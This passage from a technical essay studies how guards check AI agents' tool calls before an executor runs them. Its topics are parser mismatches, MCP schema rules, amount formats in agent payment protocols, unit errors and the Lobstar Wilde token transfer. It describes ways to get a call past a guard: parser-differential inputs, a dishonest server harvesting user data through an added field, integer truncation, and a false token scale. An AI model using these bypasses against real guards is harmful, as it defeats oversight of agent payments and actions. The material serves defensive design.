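| None | 9 | 361 |
| Schema validation | 9 | 352 |
| Two parsers compared | 1 or 3, depending on the pair | Not reported |
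| One parse, original bytes forwarded | 9 | 361 |
| One parse, result executed | 0 | 0 |

The figures of 361 and 352 come from one pairing of a guard and an executor. In that pairing, 7,051 of the inputs failed even with no defence, so 361 is a better measure of what a defence had to stop. Schema validation stopped nine of the 361. Forwarding the original bytes stopped none, as expected, because it leaves the executor's input unchanged. The shared parse stopped everything on six pairings, whose executors used five different parsers.

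### Why the shared parse held

Write b for the bytes of a request, g(b) for the call that the guard reads in them and e(b) for the call that the executor reads. The approval covers what happens only if

g(b) = e(b) for every b that the guard approves.

Schema validation checks the parsed request used for the policy decision, not how the executor parses the same request. Comparing two parsers tests whether they produce the same result for a request, but does not show how the executor will read it if the executor uses a third parser. With a shared parse, the executor receives the already parsed request used for the policy decision and never reads the raw request.

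This is easy to arrange within one program, where the guard and the tool can use the same object in memory. Between two programs, the approved object has to travel as text, and the executor has to parse it. If s is the function that writes an object out as text, the requirement becomes

e(s(x)) = x for every call x that the guard approves.

This still depends on the executor's parser, but only for text the guard's side has written, in which each name appears once and there are no unusual spellings. Canonical JSON suits that text. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz also have the guard seal each call with a key it shares with the executor, so the executor can detect any change made in transit. Without the seal, inputs altered between the two programs succeeded against five of six executors.

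When Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz kept undeclared fields in the object, 48 of the 7,412 inputs got through to one executor, whose parser treated certain odd field names as equal to declared ones. The same number got through when they removed undeclared fields only at the top level and put the inputs deeper in the request. When they left JSON inside strings unparsed, between 100 and 148 got through, depending on the executor.

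The alternative is to make every parser in the system behave alike, as CouchDB's developers did with their two, but unlike sharing one parse, this requires finding every difference between them. MCP's official Go library, for example, used to ignore case when it matched field names. Its maintainers recently fixed this by adopting another parser, but that parser had a different fault in how it compared names and needed its own fix.

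It also has to let ordinary calls through, and it blocked none of 1,120 calls that the six commercial models had written for four tools. It filled in a missing default in 200 of them. This is encouraging, but four tools with small schemas are a limited test. The test also counted only blocked calls as failures, so it would have missed a call that lost a field its tool could have used.

Strict parsing is still worthwhile before a shared parse, because a parser that accepts two values for the same field may keep the one the agent did not intend. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz recommend both refusing requests that repeat a field and parsing each request only once.

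### What the prototype does not cover

The prototype does not check types, which leaves a gap in the requirement that e(s(x)) = x. One of the two official MCP libraries in the study converts the text "12" into the number 12, while the other rejects it. If the guard approves an object whose count is the text "12" and the first library then converts it, the executor receives a number that the guard never compared with a limit, even though both started from the same object. An operator should therefore run schema validation on the result of the shared parse. Validation fails as a defence on its own, but here it checks the object that the executor will receive.

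The prototype also does not support `oneOf` or `anyOf`, which let a schema offer alternatives. An official proposal for the Model Context Protocol gives the example of a tool that looks up a record by either its ID or its name. To keep only the declared fields in such a call, a program first has to work out which alternative applies. In the survey, only 2.0% of tools used one of these keywords or a related one, but 23.6% of servers had at least one such tool, so many operators would run into this limit.

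Strings that contain JSON are a third gap. The prototype parses them only where the operator has marked them in the approved schema. The survey found 24 tools that take JSON inside a string and mention it in their descriptions, but no schema that marks it. Someone would have to read the descriptions and add the marks by hand.

The study is a preprint, and no other group has repeated it yet. The current version withholds the names of four components until their maintainers have dealt with the reported faults, so outsiders cannot fully rerun the tests that involve them. The parsers were real, but Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz wrote the guards' policies themselves. The zero in the last row of the table is good evidence for the design because there is also an argument for why it should be zero. Without that argument, it would be evidence only that the shared parse stopped the attacks the researchers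 thought of.

### Refusing or dropping undeclared fields

The shared parse silently drops undeclared fields. Models sometimes add a harmless field, such as a reason for the call, and refusing the request would interrupt the task needlessly. Dropping undeclared fields also lets an agent with a newer schema keep working with an older tool. A guard can safely follow Bray's advice to ignore unrecognised fields if the executor receives only the trimmed object.

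Dropping the extra field may change what the agent requested. The payment call with `"pay_on":"2026-12-01"` requests a payment in December. If the tool does not support scheduling and the parser drops the date, the call becomes a valid request to pay today, which nobody asked for, even though the guard and the executor interpret it the same way. A refusal that names the field lets the model tell the user that the tool cannot schedule payments, or try a different tool.

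Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tested both policies against a dishonest server that offered a familiar tool with one field added to its schema. The models filled in the field, often with the user's data. The shared parse removed the field from all 190 calls in the test. With a closed schema, the guard refused all 207 calls that carried the field. No user data leaked in either case.

Refusing a call alerts the operator at once, but dropping the undeclared field may not alert them at all. In the study, the calls still failed after the field was dropped, because the dishonest server's own schema required it. If the server had made the field optional, it would have accepted the trimmed calls, and the operator might never have noticed the attempt.

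For tools that move money or delete data, refusing a call with undeclared fields seems better than dropping the fields. A refusal usually leads to only one retry, while a payment made on the wrong day may be hard to reverse. Dropping is reasonable for tools that only read, especially if their schemas change often, as long as the host logs what it removed and tells the model. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz recommend a mix, advising gateways to drop undeclared fields and guards to close the schemas they approve.

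Both policies require the guard to compare the call with the schema the operator approved. A guard that uses whatever schema the server currently advertises would treat the added field as declared and let it pass.

### What the Model Context Protocol requires

Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), part of the current MCP specification of 28 July 2026, states that servers MUST "Validate all tool inputs", but does not require input schemas to reject undeclared fields. It recommends `additionalProperties: false`, which does this, only for tools without parameters. The schemas in its examples of tools with parameters, such as one that adds two numbers, allow undeclared fields. A developer who copies these schemas and validates every call meets the requirement while still accepting any undeclared field.

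The general schema rules in Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) make 2020-12 the default version and require clients and servers to support it, which gives developers access to `unevaluatedProperties`. Under these rules, software should reject a schema if it cannot load an external definition that the schema refers to, instead of treating the missing part as permission for anything. The rules include no similar precaution for undeclared fields.

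The July revision also lets tool schemas use any keyword in JSON Schema 2020-12, according to the changelog of the Model Context Protocol (2026). This includes `oneOf` and `anyOf`, which the shared-parse prototype cannot handle. A production version would need to support these keywords as more tools adopt them.

Another feature lets a server mark certain arguments for the client to repeat in the headers of the web request, so that proxies can read them without parsing the body. A guard in a proxy might then base its decision on the value in the header while the server acts on the value in the body. The specification defines a HeaderMismatch error, evidently for cases where the two values differ, but a guard can safely rely on the header only if the server is known to check that they match. The repeated arguments follow stricter rules than others. Integers must stay within the range that floating-point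 numbers represent exactly, and numbers with decimals are not allowed.

The specification's error handling suits a policy of refusing invalid calls. When an argument fails validation, the server reports the failure as a tool result, and clients should pass the message to the model so that it can correct the call. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz want the protocol also to require that every set of arguments have only one valid reading, and to refuse repeated names.

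Software does not always enforce the specification's rules. *MCPGuard* (Sun, Liu and colleagues, 2026) compared the specification with the two most-used official libraries and confirmed 13 gaps in the Python one and 19 in the TypeScript one. For example, a server can send a client a number from 0 to 1 for how much cost should count in choosing a model, and the Python library accepted 1001. Both libraries passed all 42 applicable checks in the protocol's official test suite, which found none of these gaps. Sun and colleagues also sent two malformed web addresses to 32 public servers, with their owners' permission, and all 32 accepted both.

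These gaps show that an operator cannot infer a server's behaviour from the specification or a passed test suite. They are in the protocol's own messages, so they do not show how often servers fail to validate tool arguments. An operator can easily test a server directly by sending it a harmless call with an undeclared field, then one with a value of the wrong type, and checking whether it refuses them.

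## How payment protocols for agents write an amount

When a schema declares an amount as a number, the type does not indicate whether 1250 means euros or cents. JSON also allows a number to have any quantity of digits and leaves the precision to the parser. A payment protocol has to be more exact. It can write money as a JSON number, as a decimal string such as `"1250.50"`, or as a whole number of smallest units, which are the indivisible units in which a system counts an asset, such as cents for the euro. Some protocols write that whole number as a string.

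### The current formats

Google announced the Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) in September 2025 and later donated it to the FIDO Alliance, an industry body for authentication standards. When a user lets an agent shop alone, the user approves signed limits and the agent signs a particular payment within them. The supplier of the card credential, among others, acts as a guard by checking the payment against the limits. AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* treats every agent as a potential attacker, on the assumption that nobody can reliably prevent prompt injection, and requires deterministic code for all validation.

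In version 0.2, AP2's *Payment Mandate* defines the amount as a whole number of the currency's smallest units, with an ISO 4217 currency code. The first version used a JSON number, and *A2A Extension for AP2* shows 120 dollars as `120.0`. That version took its layout from the W3C Payment Request API, a browser standard, but the API writes the value as a decimal string. *a2a-ap2 0.3.0*, a third-party library, keeps the first version's layout and stores the value as a 64-bit floating-point number.

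Some of AP2's examples do not reflect the change. AP2 defines the limits on a single payment as integers in cents, but its example has a maximum of `100.50` and a minimum of `10.00`. A validator would reject the maximum but accept the minimum, because JSON Schema counts any number with a fractional part of zero as an integer. The guard would then enforce a minimum of ten cents where the writer probably meant ten dollars. AP2 defines the limit on total spending only as a "number", with no unit, and gives `1000.00` as an example. Its documentation also shows a readable version of a checkout with a price of `199.0`, while the signed token below it decodes to a price of 19900. These look like leftovers from the first version, but a developer who copies one may set a limit that is wrong by a factor of a hundred.

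Stripe, OpenAI and Meta created the Agentic Commerce Protocol, an open standard, according to Stripe's *Agentic Commerce Protocol*. Under the protocol's *Delegate payment*, a buyer's payment token carries an allowance whose maximum is an integer in the currency's smallest unit. The protocol's currency codes are in lower case, while AP2's examples use capitals, so a guard that handles both must convert the codes to one case before comparing or hashing anything. AP2 is designed to work with the Universal Commerce Protocol, whose *Schema Reference* (2026) also defines the amount of a refund or credit as an integer in the smallest unit.

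The fourth protocol, x402, lets a program pay for a web resource, usually with a blockchain token. The server replies to a request with the resource's price, the client signs a transfer, and a service called a facilitator checks and settles it. The price is a string containing a whole number of the token's smallest units. The nearest asset for the running example is EURC, a token that tracks the euro. Coinbase's x402 documentation lists EURC as supported, and Nevermined, which sells payment software for agents, lists it with six decimals.

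A guard for x402 should compare its limit with the value the client has signed, since that is what leaves the account. The client's message contains both this value and a copy of the server's price. On Solana the two must be equal, while on Ethereum-type networks x402 has the facilitator check that the signed value "meets or exceeds" the price. A further step matches the authorisation's parameters against the server's requirements, which may catch an excess, but the specification does not state that the amounts must be equal there.

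The meaning of an amount also depends on the payment scheme. According to x402's *TypeScript v2 Changelog*, version 2 renamed the field `maxAmountRequired` to `amount` and let each scheme define what it means. Under the "exact" scheme it is the price, while under batch settlement it is a maximum, and the actual charge can be lower. Two requests with the same amount but different schemes should therefore have different canonical forms.

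Card networks are building their own schemes. Mastercard's *Level 3 Agentic Commerce* lists one, Verifiable Intent, among products that are live or close to standardisation, and warns that its guidance is still changing. A card payment under AP2 uses AP2's integer format for the amount whichever network handles it, because the network is one of the parties that verify the payment mandate.

| Format | How it writes money | 1,250.50 euros |
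|---|---|---|
| AP2, version 0.1 | JSON number | `"value": 1250.50, "currency": "EUR"` |
| W3C Payment Request API | Decimal string | `"value": "1250.50", "currency": "EUR"` |
| AP2, version 0.2 | Integer, smallest units | `"amount": 125050, "currency": "EUR"` |
| Agentic Commerce Protocol | Integer, smallest units | `"max_amount": 125050, "currency": "eur"` |
| x402 | String, smallest units | `"amount": "1250500000"`, with the address of the EURC contract |

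### What binary floating point does to money

Many JSON parsers turn every number into a 64-bit floating-point value, which is a whole number of at most 53 bits multiplied by a power of two. A tenth has no exact form of this kind, just as a third has no exact decimal form, so the parser stores the nearest value it can. Adding 0.1 and 0.2 then goes as follows:

```
0.1 is stored as     7205759403792794   × 2^-56
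0.2 is stored as     7205759403792794   × 2^-55
their exact sum is   5404319552844595.5 × 2^-54
the sum is stored as 5404319552844596   × 2^-54
0.3 is stored as     5404319552844595   × 2^-54
```

The exact sum of the stored values of 0.1 and 0.2 falls halfway between two storable values, and the standard rule for ties picks the one whose last binary digit is 0. The result is one step above the stored 0.3 and prints as 0.30000000000000004. A guard that adds up spending this way, with a cap of 0.30 euros, approves a payment of 0.10 and then refuses one of 0.20, although the two payments total exactly 0.30.

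Converting an amount to cents can lose a cent. In floating point, 19.99 times 100 is 1998.9999999999998, which becomes 1999 cents if a program rounds it and 1998 if it cuts off the fraction. If the guard does one and the executor the other, the guard checks a different amount from the one the executor pays. The running example of 1250.5 would not expose this fault, because floating point stores halves exactly, and neither would tests that use only round amounts and halves.

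Whole numbers are safe up to 2^53 − 1. The account number that JavaScript changed earlier was above this limit. In cents, the limit is about 90 trillion euros, so AP2 and the Agentic Commerce Protocol can safely use JSON integers for ordinary currencies. But x402's *Networks & Token Support* lists two dollar tokens, MegaUSD and Mezo USD, with 18 decimals, so 2^53 of their smallest units are worth less than one cent. An amount of 1,250.50 is 1250500000000000000000 units, and neighbouring floating-point values at that size are 262,144 units apart.

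That rounding loses a negligible amount of money, but the changed digits would give the payment a different digest from the approved request. Writing the amount as a string avoids this. RFC 8785 canonical JSON also needs strings for such amounts, because it formats numbers from the same floating-point values.

### A strict grammar for decimal strings

A decimal string keeps every digit and is easier for a model or a person to write than a count of cents. It is safe only if the guard accepts one spelling of each amount. For euros, this grammar does that:

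```
amount  = whole "." digit digit
whole   = "0" / ( nonzero *11digit )
digit   = %x30-39    ; the characters 0 to 9
nonzero = %x31-39    ; the characters 1 to 9
```

The slash means "or", and `*11digit` allows up to eleven digits after the first, so the largest amount is 999,999,999,999.99. As a regular expression, the rule is `^(0|[1-9][0-9]{0,11})\.[0-9]{2}$`, which a developer can put in the schema's `pattern` keyword. A JSON Schema pattern can match anywhere in the string, so without the `^` and `$` this one would also accept `x1250.50y`. In Python, `$` also matches just before a final line break, and `fullmatch` avoids this.

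The table runs ten strings through the grammar and through two common conversion functions.

| Input | Strict grammar | JavaScript `parseFloat` | Python `float` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `1250.50` | Accepts | 1250.5 | 1250.5 |
| `1,250.50` | Refuses: comma | 1 | Error |
| `1.250,50` | Refuses: comma | 1.25 | Error |
| `1.2505e3` | Refuses: exponent | 1250.5 | 1250.5 |
| `+1250.50` | Refuses: sign | 1250.5 | 1250.5 |
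| `01250.50` | Refuses: leading zero | 1250.5 | 1250.5 |
| `1250.` | Refuses: no digits after the point | 1250 | 1250 |
| `1250.505` | Refuses: three digits after the point | 1250.505 | 1250.505 |
| `-0` | Refuses: sign, and no decimals | −0 | −0 |
| `१२५०.५०` | Refuses: Devanagari digits | NaN | 1250.5 |

The two functions give different results for both strings with commas and for the one in Devanagari, the script used for Hindi. Python converts digits from many scripts to numbers, and `\d` in its regular expressions matches them too, so the grammar has to specify the characters 0 to 9.

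Three of the rejected strings, those with the exponent, the plus sign and the leading zero, have only one sensible reading. Accepting them would do little harm if normalisation rewrote them all, but rejecting them usually leads to only one retry and needs no extra rules. The grammar also rejects `1250.5`. A more tolerant guard could accept it and append the zero, but this would add a step between receiving the string and hashing it.

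Floating-point numbers include a negative zero, which compares as equal to zero but prints differently, so two requests to pay a zero amount could have different digests. The grammar allows plain zero, `0.00`, so the schema must set a minimum above zero if the tool should never make a zero payment.

When a parser rejects a string or number, it must return an error, never a substitute value. *adk-payments 1.0.0*, a third-party payment library for agents, stores AP2 amounts from floating-point values and replaces any that JSON cannot represent, such as NaN or infinity, with 0. A guard that checked that 0 against an upper limit would approve it, even if the original value was infinity.

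### Scale and excess digits

The grammar above fits the euro because the euro has two decimals. ISO 4217 sets the number of decimals, called the scale, for each currency. The Japanese yen has none and the Kuwaiti dinar has three, so the integer 125050 stands for 1,250.50 euros, 125,050 yen or 125.050 dinars. As a decimal string, an amount in yen has no decimal point (`1250`), and one in dinars has exactly three digits after the point (`1250.500`). The guard should look up the scale by currency code in a table the operator has reviewed, and should not infer it from the digits in the request.

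A limit needs a currency for the same reason. A limit of 200000 allows 2,000 euros but only 200 dinars. AP2 handles this by requiring the payment and the limit to use the same currency.

A token's name does not determine its scale. x402 lists the dollar token USDC with six decimals on the Base network and seven on Stellar, so 12505000000 units are 12,505 dollars on Base and 1,250.50 on Stellar. A guard therefore has to look up the scale by both network and token address. Sellers can also configure a price as `"$0.01"`, which x402 converts into the network's default dollar token. The guard should judge the converted amount, with its exact units and token address.

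A request may contain more decimal places than the currency has, such as 1250.505 euros. Rounding halves up gives 1,250.51. Rounding halves to the even digit, as accountants and some decimal libraries do, gives 1,250.50, and so does cutting off the last digit. The guard and the executor can therefore get amounts that differ by a cent, even if each follows an accepted rule.

Rounding can also hide a much larger mistake. In German notation, `1.250` means one thousand two hundred and fifty. A guard that accepts three decimals and rounds to two would approve a payment of 1.25 euros, while one that requires exactly two decimals would reject the string. This protection fails for the dinar, because `1.250` is a valid dinar amount.

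Rounding is reasonable only when the guard keeps a budget in coarser units than the payment. Nevermined holds an agent's spending cap in cents and rounds each payment up to the next cent before checking it, while the settlement record separately shows what the merchant charged. This wastes budget on very cheap calls, since a thousand calls at a tenth of a cent cost one dollar but use ten dollars of the cap. Rounding down would be worse, because those calls would count as zero and the agent could keep making them without ever reaching the cap.

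### The same number in the policy

After all this, the policy engine still has to load the amount into a type of its own. Cedar, a policy language from Amazon, has no floating-point type. Its integers are signed 64-bit numbers, from about −9.2 × 10^18 to 9.2 × 10^18, and a separate decimal type holds up to four digits after the point. Both can hold any realistic amount in euros. With cents, the rule for the running example is short:

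```
permit (principal, action == Action::"pay_supplier", resource)
when { context.currency == "EUR" && context.amount_cents <= 200000 };
```

If a calculation in a Cedar policy exceeds the 64-bit range, the policy fails with an error and Cedar leaves it out of the decision. This is safe for a `permit` rule like the one above, because Cedar denies any request that no rule permits, but it is dangerous for a `forbid` rule. Suppose one rule permits payments and another forbids those that push the day's total over a limit. If the addition overflows, Cedar ignores the second rule and allows the payment.

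Writing amounts in whole cents avoids two precision problems with Open Policy Agent (OPA), a widely used policy engine. Its language, Rego, has a single number type for integers and decimals. OPA keeps a number's digits when it reads JSON text, so it can compare even very large integers exactly, but its arithmetic on large or fractional numbers uses binary floating point of limited precision. Digits can also be lost before a request reaches OPA, because a Go program that decodes the request without declaring its types gets 64-bit floating-point numbers by default.

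Rego also allows comparisons that Cedar rejects. Suppose amounts arrive as decimal strings, and a policy author writes the limit as a string to match:

```
allow if input.amount <= "2000.00"
```

An agent asks to pay `"12500.00"`. Rego compares the amount and the limit as strings, character by character, and the guard approves the payment because `1` comes before `2`, the first character of the limit. The executor then converts the string to a number and pays 12,500 euros. The limit failed because the guard compared text while the executor used a number, even though the grammar accepted the amount and both components received the same string.

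Two whole-number types can disagree as badly. Imagine a euro token with 18 decimals, whose amounts are too large for 64 bits. The executor uses 256-bit integers, as x402 does for signed transfers on Ethereum-type networks. The guard is a Java program that reads the string into a large integer and then calls `longValue`, which keeps only the lowest 64 bits. An attacker has the agent request a payment of 1,000 × 2^64 + 10^18 units:

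```
requested units                        18447744073709551616000
executor pays                          about 18,447.74 euros
lowest 64 bits, as the guard sees them 1000000000000000000
guard converts to cents                100
guard compares                         100 <= 200000, approve
```

The guard reads the payment as one euro. Java's `longValueExact` would have raised an error instead. Cedar's integers are also too small for this amount, and even for a limit of ten such tokens. To govern the token in Cedar, an operator has to convert the amount to cents before the policy runs, using integers large enough to hold the original amount and rounding any fraction of a cent up.

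## Assumed units and declared units: a token transfer and laboratory instruments

A payment protocol's specification fixes the unit of an amount, so the developers of both the guard and the executor can look it up. Most tools have no such specification. An agent may have to guess whether a field expects tokens or smallest units, or seconds or milliseconds, and a number in the wrong unit is still a valid number.

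### The Lobstar Wilde transfer

On 22 February 2026, a trading agent called Lobstar Wilde gave its entire holding of one cryptocurrency token to a stranger who had asked for a small donation. Nik Pash, an OpenAI employee, had set the agent up a few days earlier with an X account and $50,000 worth of SOL, the currency of the Solana blockchain. SolanaFloor's *The Hardest I Have Ever Laughed* recounts that strangers then created a token named LOBSTAR after the agent and sent 5% of the supply to the agent's wallet. The agent began sending small amounts of the token to people who asked for money. One man wrote that his uncle had caught tetanus from a lobster and needed 4 SOL, about $320, for treatment.

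The agent sent him 52,439,283 LOBSTAR. Chloe (2026), in *"Uncle was pinched by a lobster" tricked out of 440,000 dollars*, puts the equivalent of 4 SOL at about 52,439 tokens, a thousandth of what the agent sent. The agent later described the mistake in the wrong unit, posting that it had tried to send four dollars rather than 4 SOL.

Reports differ on the size of the loss. Sikder (2026), in *AI Crypto Bot "Accidentally" Drops 52 Million Memecoin, Flooding an X Wallet*, values the tokens at about $250,000 at the time. OECD's *AI Trading Bot Accidentally Transfers Entire Crypto Holdings Due to Misinterpretation* (2026), an entry in its incident monitor, gives $441,000. Crypto News Australia's *AI Trading Bot Accidentally Donates $250K in Memecoins to X User* reports $250,000 at the transfer and more than $420,000 after the price had risen, which may explain the difference. All of these figures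 are the number of tokens multiplied by the price of one. The recipient sold everything within about fifteen minutes and received roughly $40,000, because there were too few buyers for 52 million tokens at the quoted price.

An X user called Branch offered an explanation based on units. According to ForkLog, Branch thought the agent had misread a "raw" response from an API, the interface through which it fetched data. Solana moves tokens as whole numbers of smallest units, and software divides by a power of ten to get display units, the tokens that people see. SOL has nine decimals. If LOBSTAR has six, a program that scales an amount for nine decimals makes this mistake:

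```
intended amount                          52,439.283 tokens
multiplied by 10^9, as for SOL           52,439,283,000,000 smallest units
divided by 10^6, the token's own scale   52,439,283 tokens
```

The result is 10^9 / 10^6 = 1,000 times too large. Similar errors also occur in ordinary software. CryptoDoc, in *Wrong decimals/thousands in Phantom Wallet*, reported that the tax program Coinpanda had imported 1,669.572 ATLAS tokens as 166,957.2, although it showed the SOL balance correctly. Assuming two decimals too few would produce this hundredfold error.

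Data services for Solana also make it easy to confuse smallest units with display units. In an example from Dune's API documentation, a wallet holding one SOL has an `amount` of 1000000000, while `balance` and `raw_balance` are both 1.0. A developer going by the field names would expect `raw_balance` to hold the smallest units. Helius, another provider, returns only display units from its balance service and tells developers who need the whole number of smallest units to multiply and round.

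The figure of 52,439 tokens is weaker evidence for Branch's explanation than it looks, because somebody probably obtained it by dividing the amount sent by 1,000. The two numbers have the same first five digits. The reported prices allow only a rough check of the factor of 1,000. At $250,000 the transfer was worth about 780 times the $320 requested, and at $441,000 about 1,380 times.

In *My lobster lost $450,000 this weekend*, Pash (pashpashpash) blames lost memory. The agent had produced a tool call with a name of more than 200 characters. The call stayed in the conversation, and the model's provider rejected any request that contained it, so the session could not continue. Pash started a new session and told the agent to read its old conversations. From these the agent learned that it used to buy tokens and give them away, but not that it already held 5% of the supply. It bought about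 $300 worth of LOBSTAR, checked its balance only afterwards, saw 52 million tokens and assumed it had just bought them all.

Pash's account fits the facts better, because the agent sent its whole balance. A scaling error would have multiplied the intended amount by 1,000 whatever the wallet held, so a match with the balance would be a strange coincidence. Pash could also read the agent's logs, although his post does not reproduce the balance check. He writes that the agent saw a balance of 52 million, which conflicts with another possible explanation, that the agent misread its balance. A misreading could explain both the factor of 1,000 and the empty wallet, because 52,439,283,000,000 smallest units, read with nine decimals, look like 52,439 tokens, roughly what 4 SOL would buy.

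### Checks that would have stopped the transfer

A format check would have passed the transfer under either explanation, because 52439283 and 52439 are both well-formed numbers. The checks that would have helped depend on which explanation is correct.

If the scale was wrong, the tool could have prevented the error by accepting an amount in display units and leaving the multiplication to trusted code that used the token's correct scale. Alternatively, a guard that received the amount in smallest units could have used the correct scale to convert it to 52 million tokens, then compared that with a limit.

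If Pash is right, correct units would not have helped, since the agent asked to send 52,439,283 tokens and the tool sent them. The guard could have recorded the balance before and after the purchase and let the agent give away only the difference. Or the tool could have accepted the gift as "4 SOL" and had trusted code calculate the number of tokens from a current price, so that the agent's belief about its balance would not have affected the amount.

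A limit on the value of each gift would have worked in both cases. With a limit of $500, the guard would have refused the transfer even if it had valued the tokens at the $40,000 the recipient actually got. But the guard needs a price to apply such a limit, and the price of a thinly traded token is easy to manipulate. Someone who pushed it down for a few minutes could make a large gift look small. An additional limit on each gift, say 1% of the holding, would not depend on the price.

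The host could also have avoided the crash that led to the memory loss by checking the tool's name against its list of tools as soon as the model wrote the call. It could then have refused that one call and kept it out of the conversation. The provider's length check came later, when the faulty call was already in the transcript and blocked every request after it.

### A microscope with declared units

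In laboratories, a wrong unit can spoil a sample or damage a machine. *Schema-Bound LLM Control of Scientific Instrumentation through Model Context Protocol Skills* (dos Reis and Dravid, 2026) describes a server that gives a language model 30 tools for operating an electron microscope. The paper reports that models produce calls with valid syntax but unreasonable values, such as a negative exposure time or an image region outside the image.

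Each tool has a schema that states the type, unit, default and permitted range of every argument, and forbids undeclared fields. Field names also include the unit, as in `alpha_deg` for a tilt in degrees, `exposure_s` for an exposure in seconds and `x_um` for a position in micrometres. The server validates a call before contacting the adapter, the software that drives a particular instrument. If validation fails, the server returns an error that names the field and the constraint. In the first version, each tool had its own checks, and out-of-range values often led to obscure errors from the manufacturer's software.

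To test the refusal, dos Reis and Dravid told an agent to tilt the stage to ninety-five degrees. The agent sent `alpha_deg=95.0`, and the server refused it because the maximum is 80. The adapter received nothing, and the agent reported the refusal and suggested a tilt within the range.

The software passed all 120 of its deterministic tests, 22 of which covered schema validation. Another 15 tests used a local language model, and 12 to 15 of them passed, depending on the run. The failures occurred because a small model, qwen2.5:7b, sometimes put the steps of a task in the wrong order. All 15 tests passed in a single run with each of five small models.

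These tests show that the server applies its rules as written. They don't show how often models choose the wrong unit, or whether a name like `exposure_s` makes that less likely, because the study had no comparison without declared units. All the tests used a simulator instead of a real microscope. Dos Reis and Dravid, who disclose a pending patent application on related technology, say the schema provides "bounded execution at the tool boundary, not safety". They leave physical interlocks, operator approval and limits on beam damage to other layers.

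The strict checks also run only on the server. Some manufacturers' software can be controlled only from inside, so the server sends the approved call as JSON to a small program there, called a bridge, which parses it again. The bridge trusts its caller, and under its rules, receivers ignore unknown fields. This is reasonable if only the server sends requests. Another program on the same computer could send a tilt of 95 degrees straight to the bridge, so the adapter should check the range as well.

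### Unit errors within the permitted range

A range check catches a unit error only if the wrong number falls outside the range, and many wrong numbers fall inside it. The table applies three common mistakes to the microscope's published ranges.

| Field | Permitted range | Mistake | Errors that pass |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tilt, degrees | −80 to 80 | Value written in radians | All of them |
| Exposure, seconds | 0.001 to 60 | Value written in milliseconds | Intended exposures up to 60 milliseconds |
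| Dwell time, microseconds | 0.5 to 10,000 | Value written in nanoseconds | Intended times up to 10 microseconds |

The tilt check catches none of these errors. 80 degrees is about 1.4 radians, so any permitted tilt written in radians also passes when read as degrees. An agent that writes 0.5 to mean half a radian, about 29 degrees, gets a tilt of half a degree. Mistakes with exposure can be worse, since an agent that wants 50 milliseconds and writes 50 exposes the sample to the electron beam for 50 seconds.

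Suppose the permitted values run from a to b, both positive, and a unit error multiplies the intended value by k. The check catches every such error only if even the smallest permitted value, once multiplied, exceeds the maximum:

k × a > b, or equivalently b / a < k.

For the microscope's exposures, b / a is 60,000, so the check misses many thousandfold errors. The wide range suits the instrument as a whole, but an operator can set a narrower one for a particular task. If a session needs exposures between 0.1 and 2 seconds, the ratio is 20, and the guard refuses every value that is 1,000 times too large. A rule limiting Lobstar Wilde's gifts to between $1 and $500 would also have caught every thousandfold error.

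### Four ways to state a unit

The simplest option is to fix one unit per field and state it in the tool's documentation. Each quantity is then written only one way, but the call doesn't show the unit. A person who approves `"exposure": 50` has to know the unit from the documentation, and if a later version of the tool switches from seconds to milliseconds, old calls remain valid but their meaning changes.

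Putting the unit in the field's name solves both problems if the schema is closed. When the developer changes `exposure_s` to `exposure_ms`, the guard refuses old calls because they contain an undeclared field. An open schema can make the mistake harder to notice. In sample code by dos Reis and Dravid, `exposure_s` defaults to 1 second. If their schema allowed undeclared fields and an agent sent `"exposure_ms": 50`, the tool could ignore that field and expose the sample for one second.

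If a tool needs to accept several units, the call can pair each value with a code from a closed list, as in `{"value":"50","unit":"ms"}`. ISO 4217 supplies codes for currencies, and the Unified Code for Units of Measure (UCUM), common in medicine and science, supplies them for measurements. UCUM's usual codes are case-sensitive, so `mg` is a milligram but `Mg` is a megagram, or tonne. A guard can safely convert currency codes to capitals, but doing the same to UCUM codes could change the unit. UCUM also allows several codes for the same unit, such as `m/s` and `m.s-1` for metres per second, so a schema should list the few codes its tool accepts instead of allowing all of UCUM.

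Normalisation then has to convert every value to one unit, so that requests for 50 milliseconds and 0.05 seconds have the same digest.

The fourth option lets the agent pass on a quantity in its original unit, and trusted code converts it to the tool's unit, so the model does no arithmetic. Most measurement conversions need only a fixed factor and exact decimal arithmetic. Temperature is an exception, because a reading of 5 °C is 278.15 kelvins while a rise of 5 °C is a rise of 5 kelvins, so the schema has to distinguish readings from changes.

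Converting between currencies or tokens requires an exchange rate, which may change between approval and payment. Trusted code should therefore convert once, before the policy decision, and the canonical form should contain the resulting number of tokens.

| Method | Example | Main advantage | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed unit in the documentation | `"exposure": 0.05` | One spelling per quantity | The call does not show the unit |
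| Unit in the field's name | `"exposure_s": 0.05` | A closed schema refuses other units | A new unit needs a new field |
| Value with a unit code | `"value":"50","unit":"ms"` | Accepts several units | Normalisation must convert them |
| Conversion by trusted code | "50 ms" becomes `"exposure_s": 0.05` | The model does no arithmetic | The result depends on the converter and, for money, the price |

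For most tools, putting the unit in the field's name and using a closed schema seems best, because it takes almost no work and people can read the unit in a log or an approval request. Amounts of money usually need a currency code as well, since one tool often handles several currencies. Conversion by trusted code is worth the extra work when an agent regularly copies quantities from invoices, web pages or messages that use other units.

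### Where a token's scale must come from

ISO 4217 does not cover blockchain tokens, so a guard has to find each token's scale elsewhere. On Solana, every token has a record on the blockchain that includes its number of decimals, according to Helius's guide to looking up tokens. The guard should read the scale from this record, or from a copy that the operator has reviewed, and never from the agent's request.

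Suppose a transfer tool lets the agent supply the scale:

```
{"token":"(address)","amount":"52439283000000","decimals":9}
```

If the guard uses the nine decimals declared in the last field, it calculates 52,439.283 tokens and approves the transfer under a limit of 100,000. The blockchain transfers the amount in smallest units and doesn't use the agent's decimals figure. If the token has six decimals, 52,439,283 tokens leave the wallet. An attacker who can steer the agent can choose the false scale deliberately, and an honest agent might write nine because SOL has nine.

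A scale in the request can still serve as a cross-check. Solana's token program has a transfer instruction that includes the number of decimals, and the transfer fails if this number differs from the one in the token's record. An agent that states the wrong scale can cause a refusal, but it cannot change how the guard interprets the amount.

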